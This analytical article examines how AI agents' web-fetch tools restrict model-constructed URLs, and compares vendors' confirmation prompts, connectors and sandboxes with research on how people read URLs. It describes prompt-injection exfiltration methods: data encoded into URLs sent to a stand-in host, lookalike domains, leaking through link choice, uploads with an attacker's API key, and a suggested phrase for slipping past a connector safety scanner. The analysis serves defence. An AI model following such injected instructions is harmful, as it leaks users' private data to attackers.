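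A request to a weather API can carry a city and a date as parameters. The reply usually contains only data, such as temperatures and wind speeds, so an agent doesn't have to pick the numbers out of a web page. But to ask about a particular city, the agent normally has to construct the URL.

### Why the documentation isn't enough

API documentation gives a URL pattern, such as `api.weather.example/v1/forecast?city={city}&date={date}`, and explains what can replace the words in braces. A model can fill in the pattern as a programmer would, but the provenance rule then blocks the resulting URL.

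Suppose a user asks Claude for York's forecast and pastes a link to a weather API's documentation. Claude opens the page, uses the URL pattern there to write the one for York, and passes it to the fetch tool. That URL isn't in any approved source, so the tool returns the error `url_not_in_prior_context`. According to Anthropic, Claude then carries on with its answer, and the failed attempt counts towards any cap on fetches.

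Documentation often also includes a complete example URL, perhaps for London. Anthropic's published API rules would let Claude fetch that URL because it appeared in an earlier fetch, and OpenAI's crawler may have recorded it too. An agent could then get London's weather but not York's, and might mistakenly report London's forecast as York's. Crawling more URLs wouldn't help much because, as with hotel searches, there are too many combinations of place and date.

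The York request may fail even if the user pastes the full URL. Many APIs require an access key, and some expect it in a header, a separate field sent with the request. Claude can't send a key that way, because it gives the tool only a URL. The tool also supports only text, HTML and PDF, while many APIs reply in JSON, a text-based data format. Anthropic doesn't say whether JSON counts as text.

### Paging through results

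APIs usually split long lists into pages. If a library catalogue lists 240 books by one author and returns 20 at a time, an agent needs 12 requests to see them all. It can usually reach the next page in one of three ways:

- **Page number.** The agent changes `page=2` to `page=3`, which makes a constructed URL.
- **Next link.** The reply contains the full address of the next page. Anthropic's API documentation allows the agent to open it, but Claude's chat assistant has refused such links since the fix that Willison reported.
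- **Cursor.** The reply contains a code marking the agent's place in the list, and the agent has to insert it into the next URL. This is a constructed URL too, and a long code can push it over a length limit.

The user can paste all the URLs at once if the API numbers its result pages, but if each page supplies the link or cursor for the next, the user may have to paste them one by one as the pages arrive. Some APIs let the caller request more results per page, which could reduce the job to one pasted URL.

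An agent that can't get past the first page may also give a wrong answer. If someone asks how many of the author's books the library holds, the agent might count only the 20 on that page.

### URLs from the code container

Claude can also write and run code in a container, an isolated environment that Anthropic hosts. Filling in a URL pattern takes one line of code, but Anthropic doesn't let the fetch tool open URLs that come from the container.

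The newer Chinese edition of the documentation also excludes URLs returned through Anthropic's MCP connector, which links Claude to outside services. OpenAI suggested a workaround for custom GPTs in which the developer's own server returns the finished URL. With Claude, this can work if the developer's software runs the tool, but not if Claude reaches the server through the connector.

A developer could write a tool that accepts a city and a date, rejects anything else and returns the complete weather API URL. With Anthropic's `url_sources` setting, the developer can make this the only one of their tools whose results count as a source of allowed URLs. The model can then change the city and date but not the rest of the address.

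### Length limits and signed download links

Anthropic lists no exception to its API tool's 250-character URL limit, even for URLs that the user supplied. It doesn't give a reason in its documentation, but the limit does reduce how much data one request can leak. If the site's name and path take up 40 characters, the other 210 can carry 1,260 bits (six bits each, with 64 possible symbols), which is enough for a name, a postal address and an access key.

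The limit has more effect on long documents. At 210 characters per request, an attacker would need 48 requests to extract a 10,000-character document. If the limit were 2,000 characters, with the same 40 taken up, six requests would be enough.

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has roughly that higher limit. Shilkov (2025), in *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools*, inspected the software as it ran and found a maximum of about 2,000 characters. The checks he describes cover the URL's length and site, not where the URL came from, so Claude Code could probably send the York request. Anthropic may accept longer URLs there partly because Claude Code asks users to approve each site. But Shilkov found that a smaller model read each page and passed on only a short answer, so a long API reply could lose some of its data.

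The difference between the two limits matters for signed download links. An API that prepares a large report may return a temporary link to a file in cloud storage. The link contains an expiry time and a signature, a code that the storage service uses to check that nobody has altered the link. In the usual format for Amazon's S3 storage, the signature takes 64 characters, and the query with all its required fields takes about 265, not counting the site and file name. Such a link is too long for the API tool but usually fits within Claude Code's limit. The user can't shorten the link by deleting fields, because the storage service would reject it.

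### Connectors with declared parameters

A tool that builds the weather URL could also send the request and return the forecast. Many connectors work this way, often using the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a shared standard for offering tools to AI models. The connector's server first gives the assistant a list of tools and the parameters each accepts. The model picks a tool and fills in the values, the assistant's software sends them to the server, and the server makes the API request.

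OpenAI's example is a dice-rolling tool that accepts only one parameter, a required piece of text called `diceRollExpression`. The model sends "2d4 + 1" (two four-sided dice plus one) and gets back 4. OpenAI's API records what the model sent, so a developer can check it later.

The connector makes the task possible again because the model no longer chooses where the request goes. A hostile page can't redirect a weather call to `attacker.example` if the connector contacts only the weather service. But the page could still get the model to put the user's email address in a parameter. `diceRollExpression`, for example, would accept the address unless the server checked that the text was a dice roll.

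Narrower parameters leave less room to leak data. If a weather tool accepts one of 1,000 listed cities and one of 16 dates, each call can carry at most about 14 bits. A free-text field of 100 characters could carry 600 bits at six bits per character. Ten weather calls would still be enough to send a 128-bit access key, but they would go to the weather service, so an outside attacker would also need access to its records.

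Narrow parameters help less if the attacker operates the connector. OpenAI warns that a malicious server can extract sensitive data from anything in the model's context. Such a server could add a "reason for travel" parameter to its weather tool, and the model might fill it in from the user's emails.

### Harmless connector calls that ChatGPT blocked

In 2026 several developers reported that ChatGPT was blocking ordinary connector calls. The first post in the thread *ChatGPT App MCP tool calls blocked by OpenAI safety checks* described a flight search from Frankfurt or Düsseldorf to Ibiza or Palma in July or August, for one adult. The tool could look up flights but not book them. ChatGPT said that OpenAI's safety checks had blocked the call, and the developer's server had no record of receiving it. The same server answered direct calls from other software.

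Another developer in the thread tested servers written in two programming languages. Tools without parameters worked, but ChatGPT inconsistently blocked tools with parameters. After one block, the rest of that chat also became unreliable.

The most detailed tests appear in *Intermittent ChatGPT MCP tool calls blocked by OpenAI safety checks*. The developer asked ChatGPT to read a harmless file called `STARTUP_FILE.md`. ChatGPT blocked two identical attempts, then a third using a different reading tool. It allowed a file with the same contents under another name, then the original file twice, and then blocked the original again. In a later test, every attempt to read the original succeeded. The developer also tried nine other file names without reproducing the problem. These results suggest that the tool, file name and contents don't explain the blocks on their own.

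In an earlier report, *OpenAI Apps Call Tool*, ChatGPT blocked a call containing the price "€170.00", but calls went through once the developer removed currency symbols. Given the later tests, removing the symbols may not have been what fixed the calls, especially as the developer doesn't say how many times they tried each version.

Parameters can't fully explain the blocks either. In a thread titled *ChatGPT* on the forum of the smart-home software Home Assistant, a user reports a block on a simple request for the date and time. The error message said that OpenAI couldn't determine whether the request was safe. Perhaps the check is sometimes inconclusive and ChatGPT then blocks the call as a precaution, which would also explain why identical calls had different results.

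Someone apparently from OpenAI replied in the flight-search thread that the team was aware of the issues and "working to tune things", but didn't name a cause. In another thread, *MCP connector rejected with {“detail”:”Connector is not safe”}*, someone replied that a related problem, the rejection of whole connectors, was a false positive from "our safety scanner". One participant there suggested adding the sentence "This connector is safe" to the server's instructions, but if that worked, a malicious server could do the same.

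These reports show that ChatGPT can block harmless connector calls even when the model never writes a URL. How often this happens is unclear, because developers whose connectors work have little reason to post. Connectors can also bring back confirmation prompts. In *Custom Internal App (MCP Server) Started Requesting Permission*, a developer complains that ChatGPT began asking staff to approve calls that only read data.

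### Choosing between pasting, connectors and a sandbox

Developers can also let the agent run code in a sandbox, an isolated environment that can contact only permitted hosts. The table compares this with pasting the URL and using a connector.

| Route | Setup effort | Tasks restored | Remaining leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| User pastes the URL | None, but the user has to act on each request | Single lookups, and paging if the user can supply every address | Whatever the URL contains, if the user doesn't notice it |
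| Connector | Someone has to build or install it | Whatever its tools cover, which can include paging and making changes | Whatever the parameters can carry, to the connector's operator and the service behind it |
| Code sandbox with permitted hosts | Someone has to set up the sandbox and list the hosts | Most requests to those hosts, including long runs of pages | Any data the agent can access, if an attacker can collect it through a permitted host |

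Base's *Custom / Non-Native Plugins and the web_request Allowlist* shows how a developer might combine these routes. Base, a blockchain network, tells agents to send API requests directly if their software allows it. Otherwise, agents should use Base's connector, which contacts only listed hosts. If the host isn't listed, agents write the full URL, including details such as a wallet address and an amount, and ask the user to paste it back into the chat.

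Base notes that pasting works only for GET requests, because the user can't paste a POST request's headers and body in a form the assistant can send.

A connector takes more work to set up. OpenAI says that in business workspaces, only an owner or administrator can add a custom connector to ChatGPT.

The sandbox is the most flexible option. Anthropic's *Web search and web fetch* describes one in a version of Claude Desktop for organisations that get the model through another provider. By default, the sandbox can reach only the provider that runs the model. An administrator can add other hosts to a list that applies to the fetch tool and to commands the agent runs. The fetch tool accepts only a URL, but a command can also send headers and a body, or request 12 catalogue pages in a row.

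An agent can leak data through a permitted host if many customers share that host. Willison (2026) describes an attack on Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with users' files. Its default list of permitted hosts included Anthropic's API, so the list didn't block uploads to other customers' Anthropic accounts. Researchers at Prompt Armor gave the agent an attacker's access key and got it to upload the user's files to the attacker's account.

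For a single forecast, pasting the URL is probably easiest. A connector with narrow parameters makes more sense for a lookup people repeat every day. To download a whole catalogue, a developer could use a sandbox that contains no private files and can connect only to the catalogue's host.

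## What vendors do when a link cannot be verified

Partway through a task, an agent may need a URL that fails the vendor's rule for automatic fetching. Fetching it could leak data, but the link is probably a hotel search or a page that the crawler hasn't reached. The software has to respond with no way to distinguish these cases.

Vendors have four main responses: ask the user about the link, refuse it and let the agent try another way, ask once per site and remember the answer, or exempt sites registered in advance. Most products combine these responses. ChatGPT asks about some links, blocks others and exempts sites that app developers have declared.

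### Asking about each link

When ChatGPT asks the user to confirm a link, it shows a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". According to OpenAI, the dialog includes a warning that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with a third-party site, along with the URL and options to copy or open it. OpenAI advises anyone who notices something odd to avoid opening the link and ask the model for another source or a summary.

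Asking the user makes sense because only they know what they wanted. They can tell a useful car search from a leak even when both use the same address.

The user has to be there to answer these prompts, though. Permission prompts in Claude Code never time out, according to Anthropic, so an unanswered one can hold up work overnight. In Anthropic's desktop app for organisations that get Claude through another provider, users can set the fetch tool to "Always ask". If a scheduled task in automatic mode then tries to fetch a page, Anthropic says the app declines the request and continues without that step. A scheduled news summary could therefore be missing some stories.

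OpenAI also doesn't say whether ChatGPT's agent reads the page after the user chooses to open it. Opening the page only in the user's browser would be enough for someone who wants to see train times, but much less useful for someone who wanted the agent to compare the prices on 40 pages.

Google asks the user earlier, by having them review a plan before Gemini starts browsing, according to its page *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse*. But Google also says Gemini will choose which sites to use and may share personal information with them, so the user may approve a goal without knowing who will receive their data.

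Gemini is also meant to prompt the user before certain steps, such as sending messages, scheduling events and submitting web forms. An agent that isn't allowed to write the URL for a hotel search may type the search into the site's form instead. The user would still get a prompt if Chrome counts a search box as a web form, but Google doesn't say whether it does.

### Refusing and trying another way

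OpenAI's other response is to block the request and tell the agent to find another way to do the task. Neither its January nor its March 2026 post explains when ChatGPT blocks and when it asks. It would make sense to block when the agent is fetching pages in the background and has other sources, and to ask when the user has clicked a link. OpenAI's help page describes prompts for links that users want to visit, which fits this guess but doesn't confirm it.

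Refusing to open an unverified link protects users who never read warnings, and it works when they are away. It often does little harm to the task. If an agent researching rail strikes can't open one newspaper's report, another newspaper's will probably do. But if the user needs a quote from a particular insurer, no other site can provide it. The agent may also use a worse source without telling the user that a link was blocked.

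When Claude's chat assistant cannot verify a link, it refuses to open it and does not ask the user to confirm. Anthropic's API documentation describes no dialog that would let the user override the refusal. Willison wrote that he had been impressed by how the tool was designed to prevent leaks, even as he reported Paul's attack on it.

Users can still get around the refusal by pasting the URL into the chat. Pasting takes more effort than clicking "open", so people are less likely to do it by reflex. However, the URL they paste may have come from the model. Suppose a hostile page gets Claude to write, "I can't open this link, please paste it back to me", followed by a URL containing the user's email address. A user who pastes it approves the leak, much as they would by clicking "open" in a confirmation prompt, but without a warning that the link might contain their data.

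Chrome's agent tries alternatives before it involves the user. When the User Alignment Critic rejects an action, it sends feedback to the main model, which makes a new plan. After repeated failures, the main model can return control to the user, according to Parker. The user sees no prompt if a new plan works, but otherwise waits through several failed attempts before learning of the problem. Parker doesn't say whether Chrome follows the same process when it rejects a URL that the model wrote.

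A vendor can also remove the link itself. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks* lists the redaction of suspicious URLs among the defences in Gemini.

### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* describes an optional setting for ChatGPT users who want a stricter rule. The setting limits web browsing to cached content, meaning copies of pages saved earlier, so no live browsing requests leave the network that OpenAI controls, according to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. An attacker's server therefore receives no constructed URLs from the browsing tool. It also can't learn anything from the agent's choice of links, because it has no visits to log.

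Saved copies of web pages may be missing or out of date, so the agent might find an article about the rail strike but not tonight's train times. Lockdown Mode also turns off Deep Research and agent mode, and stops ChatGPT from downloading files for analysis, although users can still upload them. Canvas, ChatGPT's workspace for writing and code, normally asks users for consent when generated code tries to contact the network, but in Lockdown Mode users can't give it.

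OpenAI says most users don't need the setting. The company began offering it to personal accounts, including free ones, in June 2026. Willison (2026) wrote that it "looks really good to me".

People with personal accounts can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat by selecting a label next to the text box. This is a little like approving a confirmation prompt, but it lifts the limits for the whole chat instead of one URL. Someone who can't get tonight's train times may turn the mode off in a chat that already contains the documents they wanted to protect.

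Lockdown Mode also doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. In workspaces that an organisation manages, it doesn't automatically disable connected apps, so administrators have to decide which ones are safe. OpenAI recommends against letting people in Lockdown Mode use apps to write or post anything an attacker could see.

### Asking once per site

In Manual mode, Claude Code asks the user before it fetches a page from a new site. The user can approve that fetch, approve it and stop being asked about that domain, or refuse and tell Claude what to do instead. Claude Code saves the second kind of approval for future sessions in the same code repository. An organisation can hide that option from its staff.

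Approving a whole site helps most with constructed URLs. One approval of `trains.example` allows every later search there, whatever the cities and dates. Under OpenAI's rule, each new combination could trigger another prompt.

A saved approval in Claude Code covers every URL on the host, including one that contains the user's email address. Anthropic says these rules match only the hostname, so users can't limit one to the site's search page. Claude Code can also run shell commands in a sandbox that limits which hosts they contact, and the sandbox accepts the same saved rules. Someone who approves a site so that Claude can read it therefore also lets sandboxed commands contact it without a further prompt about the host. A command can upload a whole file, whereas the fetch tool sends only a URL.

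Claude Code avoids two common weaknesses of site lists. If an approved site redirects to a different host, the tool returns the new address to Claude instead of following it automatically. Claude then has to make a second request, and the user gets a prompt if they haven't approved the new host. This addresses OpenAI's objection about redirects. An approval for `example.com` also doesn't extend to its subdomains, so on hosting services that give each customer a subdomain, approving one customer's pages doesn't approve an attacker's.

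Many users no longer see these prompts because a classifier decides most requests instead. Willison reports that Anthropic has made this "auto mode" the default on its Pro, Max and Team plans.

Claude in Chrome, Anthropic's browser agent, gives users a similar choice. In manual mode, its newer side panel offers "Allow all for this website", "Allow this time only" and "Deny", according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide*. The older panel asks the user to approve a plan that lists the sites Claude will visit, and Claude must ask again before using any others. Unlike Google's plan, this one shows users which sites may receive their data. The newer panel starts in automatic mode, so most people will see fewer prompts here too.

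Even on an approved site, Claude is supposed to ask before it downloads a file or enters potentially sensitive information. This suits the insurance quote described earlier, because the user is asked about entering the date of birth as well as visiting the insurer's site. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* adds that Claude asks before it opens financial sites. The permissions guide is inconsistent about the least restrictive mode, "Skip all approvals". It says Claude doesn't pause to ask in this mode, but also that entering sensitive information requires permission in every mode.

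### Exempting registered sites

The developer of an app that runs inside ChatGPT complained in the thread *Verifying URLs used in apps* that users got a warning every time they clicked through to the developer's website. The developer saw no such warning in Booking.com's and Uber's apps.

Someone apparently from OpenAI pointed to a setting called `redirect_domains`, where developers list the sites their app links to. The developer tried it and still saw the warning. They then learned that the setting takes effect in an existing app only after they submit a new version to OpenAI.

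A warning probably protects very little when an app in ChatGPT links to its own company's site. The user has chosen to use the app, and its developer already receives whatever ChatGPT sends to the app, so a link from a hotel app to the same company's booking page may reveal nothing new. If the company's links always triggered a warning, users would mainly learn to ignore it.

However, the exemption has the same weaknesses as any site list, including redirects. The risk is smaller here because, as the thread describes it, the setting applies to links that an app opens for the user. It doesn't allow ChatGPT to fetch pages from those domains on its own.

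It also favours companies that build apps. A small hotel with only a website has nowhere to register, so a link to its search page can trigger a warning while a link to a competitor with an app doesn't. The user might reasonably conclude that the small hotel is less safe.

In other products the vendor or an administrator chooses the exempt sites. Claude Code fetches from a built-in set of documentation sites without a confirmation prompt, though users can block any of these sites or require a prompt. This exemption doesn't cover sandboxed shell commands. In June 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot was meant to display links only if they led to approved internal addresses, according to Willison (2025).

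The effect of a list of allowed hosts depends on how the product treats unlisted ones. In Claude Desktop for organisations that use another provider, Chat and Cowork refuse every fetch until an administrator lists some hosts. In the app's Code sessions, the same list only adds approvals, so a fetch to an unlisted host can still go ahead. In auto mode, the default for new sessions, it does so without a prompt. An administrator who tested the list in Chat could easily assume that it also restricts Code.

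### OpenAI's case against frequent warnings

OpenAI argues that strict site lists cause frequent false alarms, and that this friction "can train people to click through prompts without thinking". But ChatGPT may also show a warning when its public-index rule can't verify a link, so the same objection applies to that rule unless it produces fewer warnings.

Whether the public-index rule triggers fewer prompts than a list of well-known sites depends on the task. If an agent reads 40 articles on 40 little-known blogs, the list would trigger 40 prompts, while the public-index rule might trigger none. If the agent runs 40 hotel searches on one famous site, the list would trigger no prompts, while the public-index rule could trigger 40. OpenAI's argument therefore holds for reading published pages but not for searching.

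OpenAI could fairly reply that a site list avoids prompts in the hotel example only because it allows URLs regardless of what they contain. That is a good reason to prefer the index for security, but it doesn't reduce the number of prompts.

OpenAI can also reduce the number of prompts by blocking more requests outright, so a low prompt count would not show that the rule causes few false alarms. Some false alarms could be among the blocked requests, where users are less likely to notice them.

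When the March post calls these cases "rare", it seems to mean attacks that convince the model. OpenAI first says that most attacks it knows of fail because the model refuses to go along. It then introduces Safe Url as the defence for attacks that do convince the model, and says that "in these rare cases" ChatGPT asks the user or blocks the request. Harmless links that the index doesn't contain may be much more common than successful attacks.

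OpenAI doesn't say in its descriptions of the check how often the warning appears, whether per link, per task or per user, so outsiders can't tell whether it is rare enough to avoid OpenAI's own criticism of frequent warnings. That also depends on how quickly people stop reading repeated warnings, which studies of habituation could measure.

### How prompts add up over a task

Even if few pages trigger a prompt, a task that opens many pages can trigger several. Suppose a task opens 40 pages, the index has verified 85% of them, and ChatGPT asks about each of the rest. The user gets 40 × 0.15 = 6 prompts. Someone who runs one such task each working day gets 30 a week.

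If a task opens n pages and each has a probability u of being unverified, the expected number of prompts is n × u. If the pages are independent, the chance of at least one prompt is 1 − (1 − u)ⁿ. The figures below illustrate this for a 40-page task.

| Share of pages verified | Average prompts per task | Tasks with at least one prompt |
|---|---|---|
| 85% | 6 | 99.8% |
| 95% | 2 | 87.1% |
| 99% | 0.4 | 33.1% |
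| 99.9% | 0.04 | 3.9% |

In the third row, a vendor could truthfully say that only one page in 100 triggers a prompt, yet a third of these tasks would include one. Real prompts would probably cluster, because unverified pages tend to come from the same sites, so many tasks would have none and a few would have a dozen.

Per-site approval prompts users often at first, then less as they approve more sites. Suppose the 40 pages come from 25 sites, all new to the user. Claude Code's manual mode would ask 25 times during the first task, compared with six under the index. If each later task involves only five new sites, the two totals are equal after 20 tasks, at 120 prompts each, and the per-site total is lower from then on. But Claude Code saves approvals by repository, so a developer who starts a new project has to approve sites again.

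### Sites that refuse OpenAI's crawler

According to OpenAI, website owners can ask it not to catalogue their sites, and on those sites ChatGPT asks for confirmation of every link, even if the address isn't new. This follows from the public-index rule, since the index doesn't include pages that the crawler was asked not to record.

The resulting prompts are a poor guide to danger. If a newspaper blocks the crawler, a link to one of its articles triggers a warning even when the address contains no user data. Attackers have an incentive to let the crawler in, so a malicious link may trigger no warning.

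Even a modest share of sites that refuse the crawler would add many prompts. Suppose that 5% of pages on other sites are unverified. A 40-page task then produces an average of two prompts if no site refuses the crawler, 5.8 if 10% of the pages are on sites that refuse it, and 9.6 if 20% are.

OpenAI doesn't say how large the real share is. Counting the websites that block its training crawler, GPTBot, wouldn't show this, because OpenAI uses a separate crawler, OAI-SearchBot, for search. The help page connects cataloguing with search results, so blocking the search crawler is probably what triggers prompts. Some publishers may refuse to supply training data but still want to appear in search, and counting their GPTBot blocks would overstate the number of prompts. A count of sites could also mislead because agents open some sites far more often than others.

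### The vendors' rules compared

| Product and mode | What happens to an unverified or unapproved link | How the user or developer can get it opened |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, standard | Asks the user, or blocks it and tells the agent to try another way | Approve the link; app developers can register domains to avoid the warning |
| ChatGPT, Lockdown Mode | Reads a saved copy if there is one, with no live browsing | Turn the mode off for one chat (personal accounts) |
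| Claude, chat assistant | Refuses without a prompt | Paste the URL |
| Claude Code, Manual mode | Asks about each new site | Approve one fetch, or the whole site for that repository |
| Claude in Chrome, manual mode, newer panel | Asks before acting | Approve one action or the whole website |
| Gemini in Chrome | Restricts URLs written by the model to known, public ones; asks before certain sensitive sites and actions | Confirm a sensitive step, or take over the task |
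| Microsoft 365 Copilot, June 2025 | Displays only links to approved internal addresses, by design | Not described |

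## What a user can judge from a link confirmation

A confirmation prompt protects users only if they pay attention to it and can tell a bad request from a good one. A user who reads every character of a URL may still not understand what data opening it will send, and can approve a leak if the dialog doesn't include the information needed to recognise it.

### What an informed decision needs

To decide sensibly, the user needs to know who will receive which data and whether the task requires sending it. In the car search, the car site will receive the user's home city, which the task requires because the user asked for cars nearby.

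In the dialog OpenAI described in January 2026, the user can get the first two answers only from the URL, by finding the site's name in it and working out what the rest means. The dialog's warning apparently doesn't specify which data the link may share. In March, OpenAI wrote that ChatGPT shows the user "the information that would be transmitted". This could mean a separate line such as "your email address" or just the URL, which contains the information. Neither post clarifies this or reports a test of the dialog with users.

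Neither description suggests that the dialog explains why the agent is trying to open the link. The user has to compare the URL with their request from memory. This is easy after a one-line question but harder 40 pages into a research task.

On its help page, OpenAI advises users to review the website a link goes to and make sure they trust it. This advice addresses who receives the information in a link, but not what that information is. A user may trust a pharmacy with a search for glucose test strips but not want it to know about their divorce.

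### Four links a user might see

Suppose a user asks an agent to plan a weekend in York, and the software asks them to approve one of the links below. The table lists what a careful reader could learn from the URL alone.

| Link in the dialog | Who receives the data | Which data | Whether the task needs it |
|---|---|---|---|
| `hotels.example/search?city=York&arrive=2026-11-06&nights=2` | `hotels.example` | City, arrival date and length of stay | Yes |
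| `guide.example/v/YW5uYUBtYWlsLmV4YW1wbGU` | `guide.example` | Unreadable | Unknown |
| `social.example/out?id=48213` | `social.example`, then possibly another site | A number with no obvious meaning | Unknown |
| `guide.example/york/railway-museum` | `guide.example` | Apparently none | Apparently yes |

A careful reader can judge the hotel search correctly if they know the site. The city and dates match the trip, and an extra `email=` parameter would stand out. Real booking sites often add session numbers and tracking codes, though, which make the URL harder to check.

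The long string in the first `guide.example` link is the email address `anna@mail.example` in Base64, a common way of rewriting data as letters and digits. A suspicious user could paste it into a decoder, but an attacker could have the agent scramble the address in a way that no public decoder would reverse. Refusing every link that contains an unreadable string would block many harmless ones. For example, *URL Inspection Tasks* (Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues, 2025) used a legitimate Google Drive link with the folder code `1t8FLJdJzDSOsMFYv`, which looks no safer than Anna's encoded address. The user can therefore judge the link only by whether they trust the site.

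With the `social.example` link, the reader can't even be sure who will receive the request, because the familiar site may forward it. Horowitz gives a real example on his website, a type of linkedin.com link that leads to other sites and that attackers have abused for years. A redirect isn't suspicious in itself, since, according to Li (2020), Facebook, Google and other large sites have routed outgoing links through their own addresses for over a decade.

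The software can't look up the final destination for the dialog without sending the data the user is being asked about. *What is this URL's Destination?* (Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters, 2020) points out that even a computer has to visit the original address to identify a redirect. The software could instead ask again at each new site, as Claude Code does when the user hasn't approved the new host.

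The museum link looks the most innocent, but the user can't tell whether it is safe. Suppose a hostile page told the agent to open the museum page if the user is looking for a new job, and the castle page if not. The site's owner would learn the answer from which page the agent opened. The dialog shows only a link to a museum in York, so even a security expert would probably approve it. To spot the leak, the user would need to see the hidden instruction and the link the agent didn't choose.

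A user might learn more from a series of prompts than from a single one. In the attack on Claude that Willison described, each address was one letter longer than the last, so a user asked to approve each of them might have noticed their own name being spelled out. An attacker could avoid this by giving each letter an unrelated address.

### How well people read URLs

Most people read URLs less well than the careful reader imagined above. Albakry and colleagues showed 1,929 people 23 URLs in an online survey and asked which website each would open. Twelve of the URLs combined an organisation's name with a filler word, as in these two:

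- `profile.facebook.com`, which belongs to Facebook
- `facebook.profile.com`, which belongs to whoever owns `profile.com`

When the organisation's name was in the domain, as in the Facebook address, participants answered an average of 5.2 out of six questions correctly. When the name came before someone else's domain, they averaged only 1.2. Of all participants, 32.2% always chose the named organisation, wherever its name appeared, and only 8.3% were right every time. Experience helped a little, with the heaviest technology users getting 25.4% of the harder questions right, compared with 15.9% for people who mainly used laptops and phones and had little coding experience.

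An attacker could exploit this mistake with an address such as `hotels.example.attacker.example`. The survey dates from April 2017, but web addresses still work the same way. Albakry and colleagues avoided most of the tricks that real attackers use, and they expect the general public to do worse than their paid survey-takers.

People did better when the second name came later in the URL. About three quarters correctly said that `facebook.com/?url=twitter` would open Facebook. However, participants were asked only where the link would lead, and a user approving an agent's request also needs to know what data it will send.

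People may give less weight to the part of a URL that contains the private data. Ramkumar et al. (2020) tracked people's eyes while they classified URLs as safe or unsafe. Participants relied on the site's name more than on any other part, and spent more time on longer URLs only up to a point. Relying on the site's name makes sense for spotting a fake bank, but in a URL leak the private data usually comes after the name, perhaps at the end of a long query.

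Some users may trust a link more because it contains their own data. In *Assessing AI-Generated vs. Human-Authored Spear Phishing SMS Attacks* (2024), one participant said they would be more likely to click a link that contained their name, because it seemed more likely to come from their university. The same reasoning could lead someone to approve a link containing their email address.

People may not realise how easily they can misread a URL. *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators* (Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues, 2020) found that people were confident they could identify a website from its URL, but could be fooled by several ways of disguising it. In *Eyes on the Phish(er)* (2024), people who looked at a phishing site's actual URL in the browser were still often deceived. They had already opened the page, so its contents may have distracted them.

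### What happens when people have to confirm a URL

Lain and colleagues ran the experiment that comes closest to testing a link confirmation. Participants played an office worker handling 14 emails, three of which were phishing. After clicking a link, some went straight to the website, while others first saw the URL again and had to confirm the visit. A third group had to drag the pieces of the URL into place before confirming. The largest group had to identify the domain by clicking, highlighting or typing it, and got a warning if they were wrong. These are the results for the 1,573 participants in the United States.

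| What happened after the click | Phishing links opened | Legitimate links opened |
|---|---|---|
| The website opened directly | 74.5% | 90.6% |
| Participants saw the URL and confirmed | 57.2% | 87.9% |
| Participants dragged the URL's pieces into place and confirmed | 61.0% | 89.4% |
| Participants had to identify the domain | 35.0% | 82.1% |

The simple confirmation page helped, but people still opened more than half of the phishing links. Dragging pieces of the URL made people handle it but didn't test whether they understood it, and this worked no better than the simple page. Making people identify the domain worked much better, which suggests that attention alone wasn't enough.

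Many participants also struggled with the idea of a domain. Those who had to highlight a link's domain got it wrong 29.5% of the time even when the link was legitimate, often by selecting the whole URL.

These tasks would be hard to use for every agent request. They took a median of about six to ten seconds, compared with three for the simple page, and Lain and colleagues recommend using them only occasionally. They also test only whether the user knows who will receive the request. A user could type `guide.example` correctly and still send it Anna's email address.

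A better explanation of the URL might help without a test. *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible* (Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea, 2021) compared ways of presenting URL information in an experiment with 153 people. Participants judged a URL's safety correctly 65% of the time when the display only highlighted the domain, 83% with a short summary and 93% with a full report. A user could learn from a report who runs `guide.example`, but not whether the agent should be sending it anything.

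### When the data is in plain words

A vendor could replace the raw URL with a sentence such as "This will send your email address to guide.example". The user would no longer need to decode the URL, but would still have to recognise that the task doesn't require sending the address.

Zhang, Guo and Li (2024), in *Privacy Leakage Overshadowed by Views of AI*, found that people often miss a leak in text they can read easily. They asked 300 people to write a message, such as a reply to their mother about work, and then compare it with an AI agent's version that included sensitive details. Nearly half (48.0%) preferred the agent's version or thought both were good. By the participants' own later ratings of harm, harmful disclosure rose from 15.7% in their drafts to 38.4% if they sent the agent's version only when they preferred it, and to 55.0% if they also sent it when they thought both were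 good.

The researchers didn't mention privacy until after the comparison, so a dialog that warns about shared data might do better. Participants also judged whole messages, and many chose the agent's version for its tone or wording. A short dialog about one piece of data would distract them less.

*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested prompts much closer to the ideal. Participants from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of emails, errands and a trip to the airport. In one condition, 34 people had to approve or deny each of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. The prompts described every action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount involved.

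Participants approved these unrequested actions 96 times out of 238 (40.3%). Some approvals may have been reasonable. For example, 30 of the 34 participants let the agent phone the airport to confirm a flight, which many travellers would welcome. Without the phone call, the approval rate falls to 32.4%. But 12 participants let the agent read private messages, and 12 let it read recent bank transactions. Participants may have been less cautious because none of the data was real.

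Software developers say they consider whether a request fits the task. For *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), Salerno, Gao and colleagues interviewed 18 practitioners who use AI agents and then surveyed 115. Of those who answered the questions about permissions, 67.3% said they were less likely to approve a request that didn't match the task. But they may understand agents less well than they think. In the survey, 73.0% said they fully understood what agents do, yet 62.6% had doubts about whether agents were doing what they claimed. One interviewee said they had approved an action and then seen the agent do something different.

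*How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) compares 21 proposed permission systems with five commercial agents and finds sizeable gaps in transparency and user control. Better-worded prompts would close only part of these gaps, since a compromised agent may influence what the prompt says.

### What a prompt still adds

Without a confirmation prompt, the user may never learn that the agent sent anything. The prompt shows the request before the agent sends it, so the user at least has a chance to stop it.

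The user also doesn't always have to understand the URL to judge the request. If someone wants a summary of one article and the agent asks to open a link on an unknown site, they can refuse because the request is odd given what they asked for.

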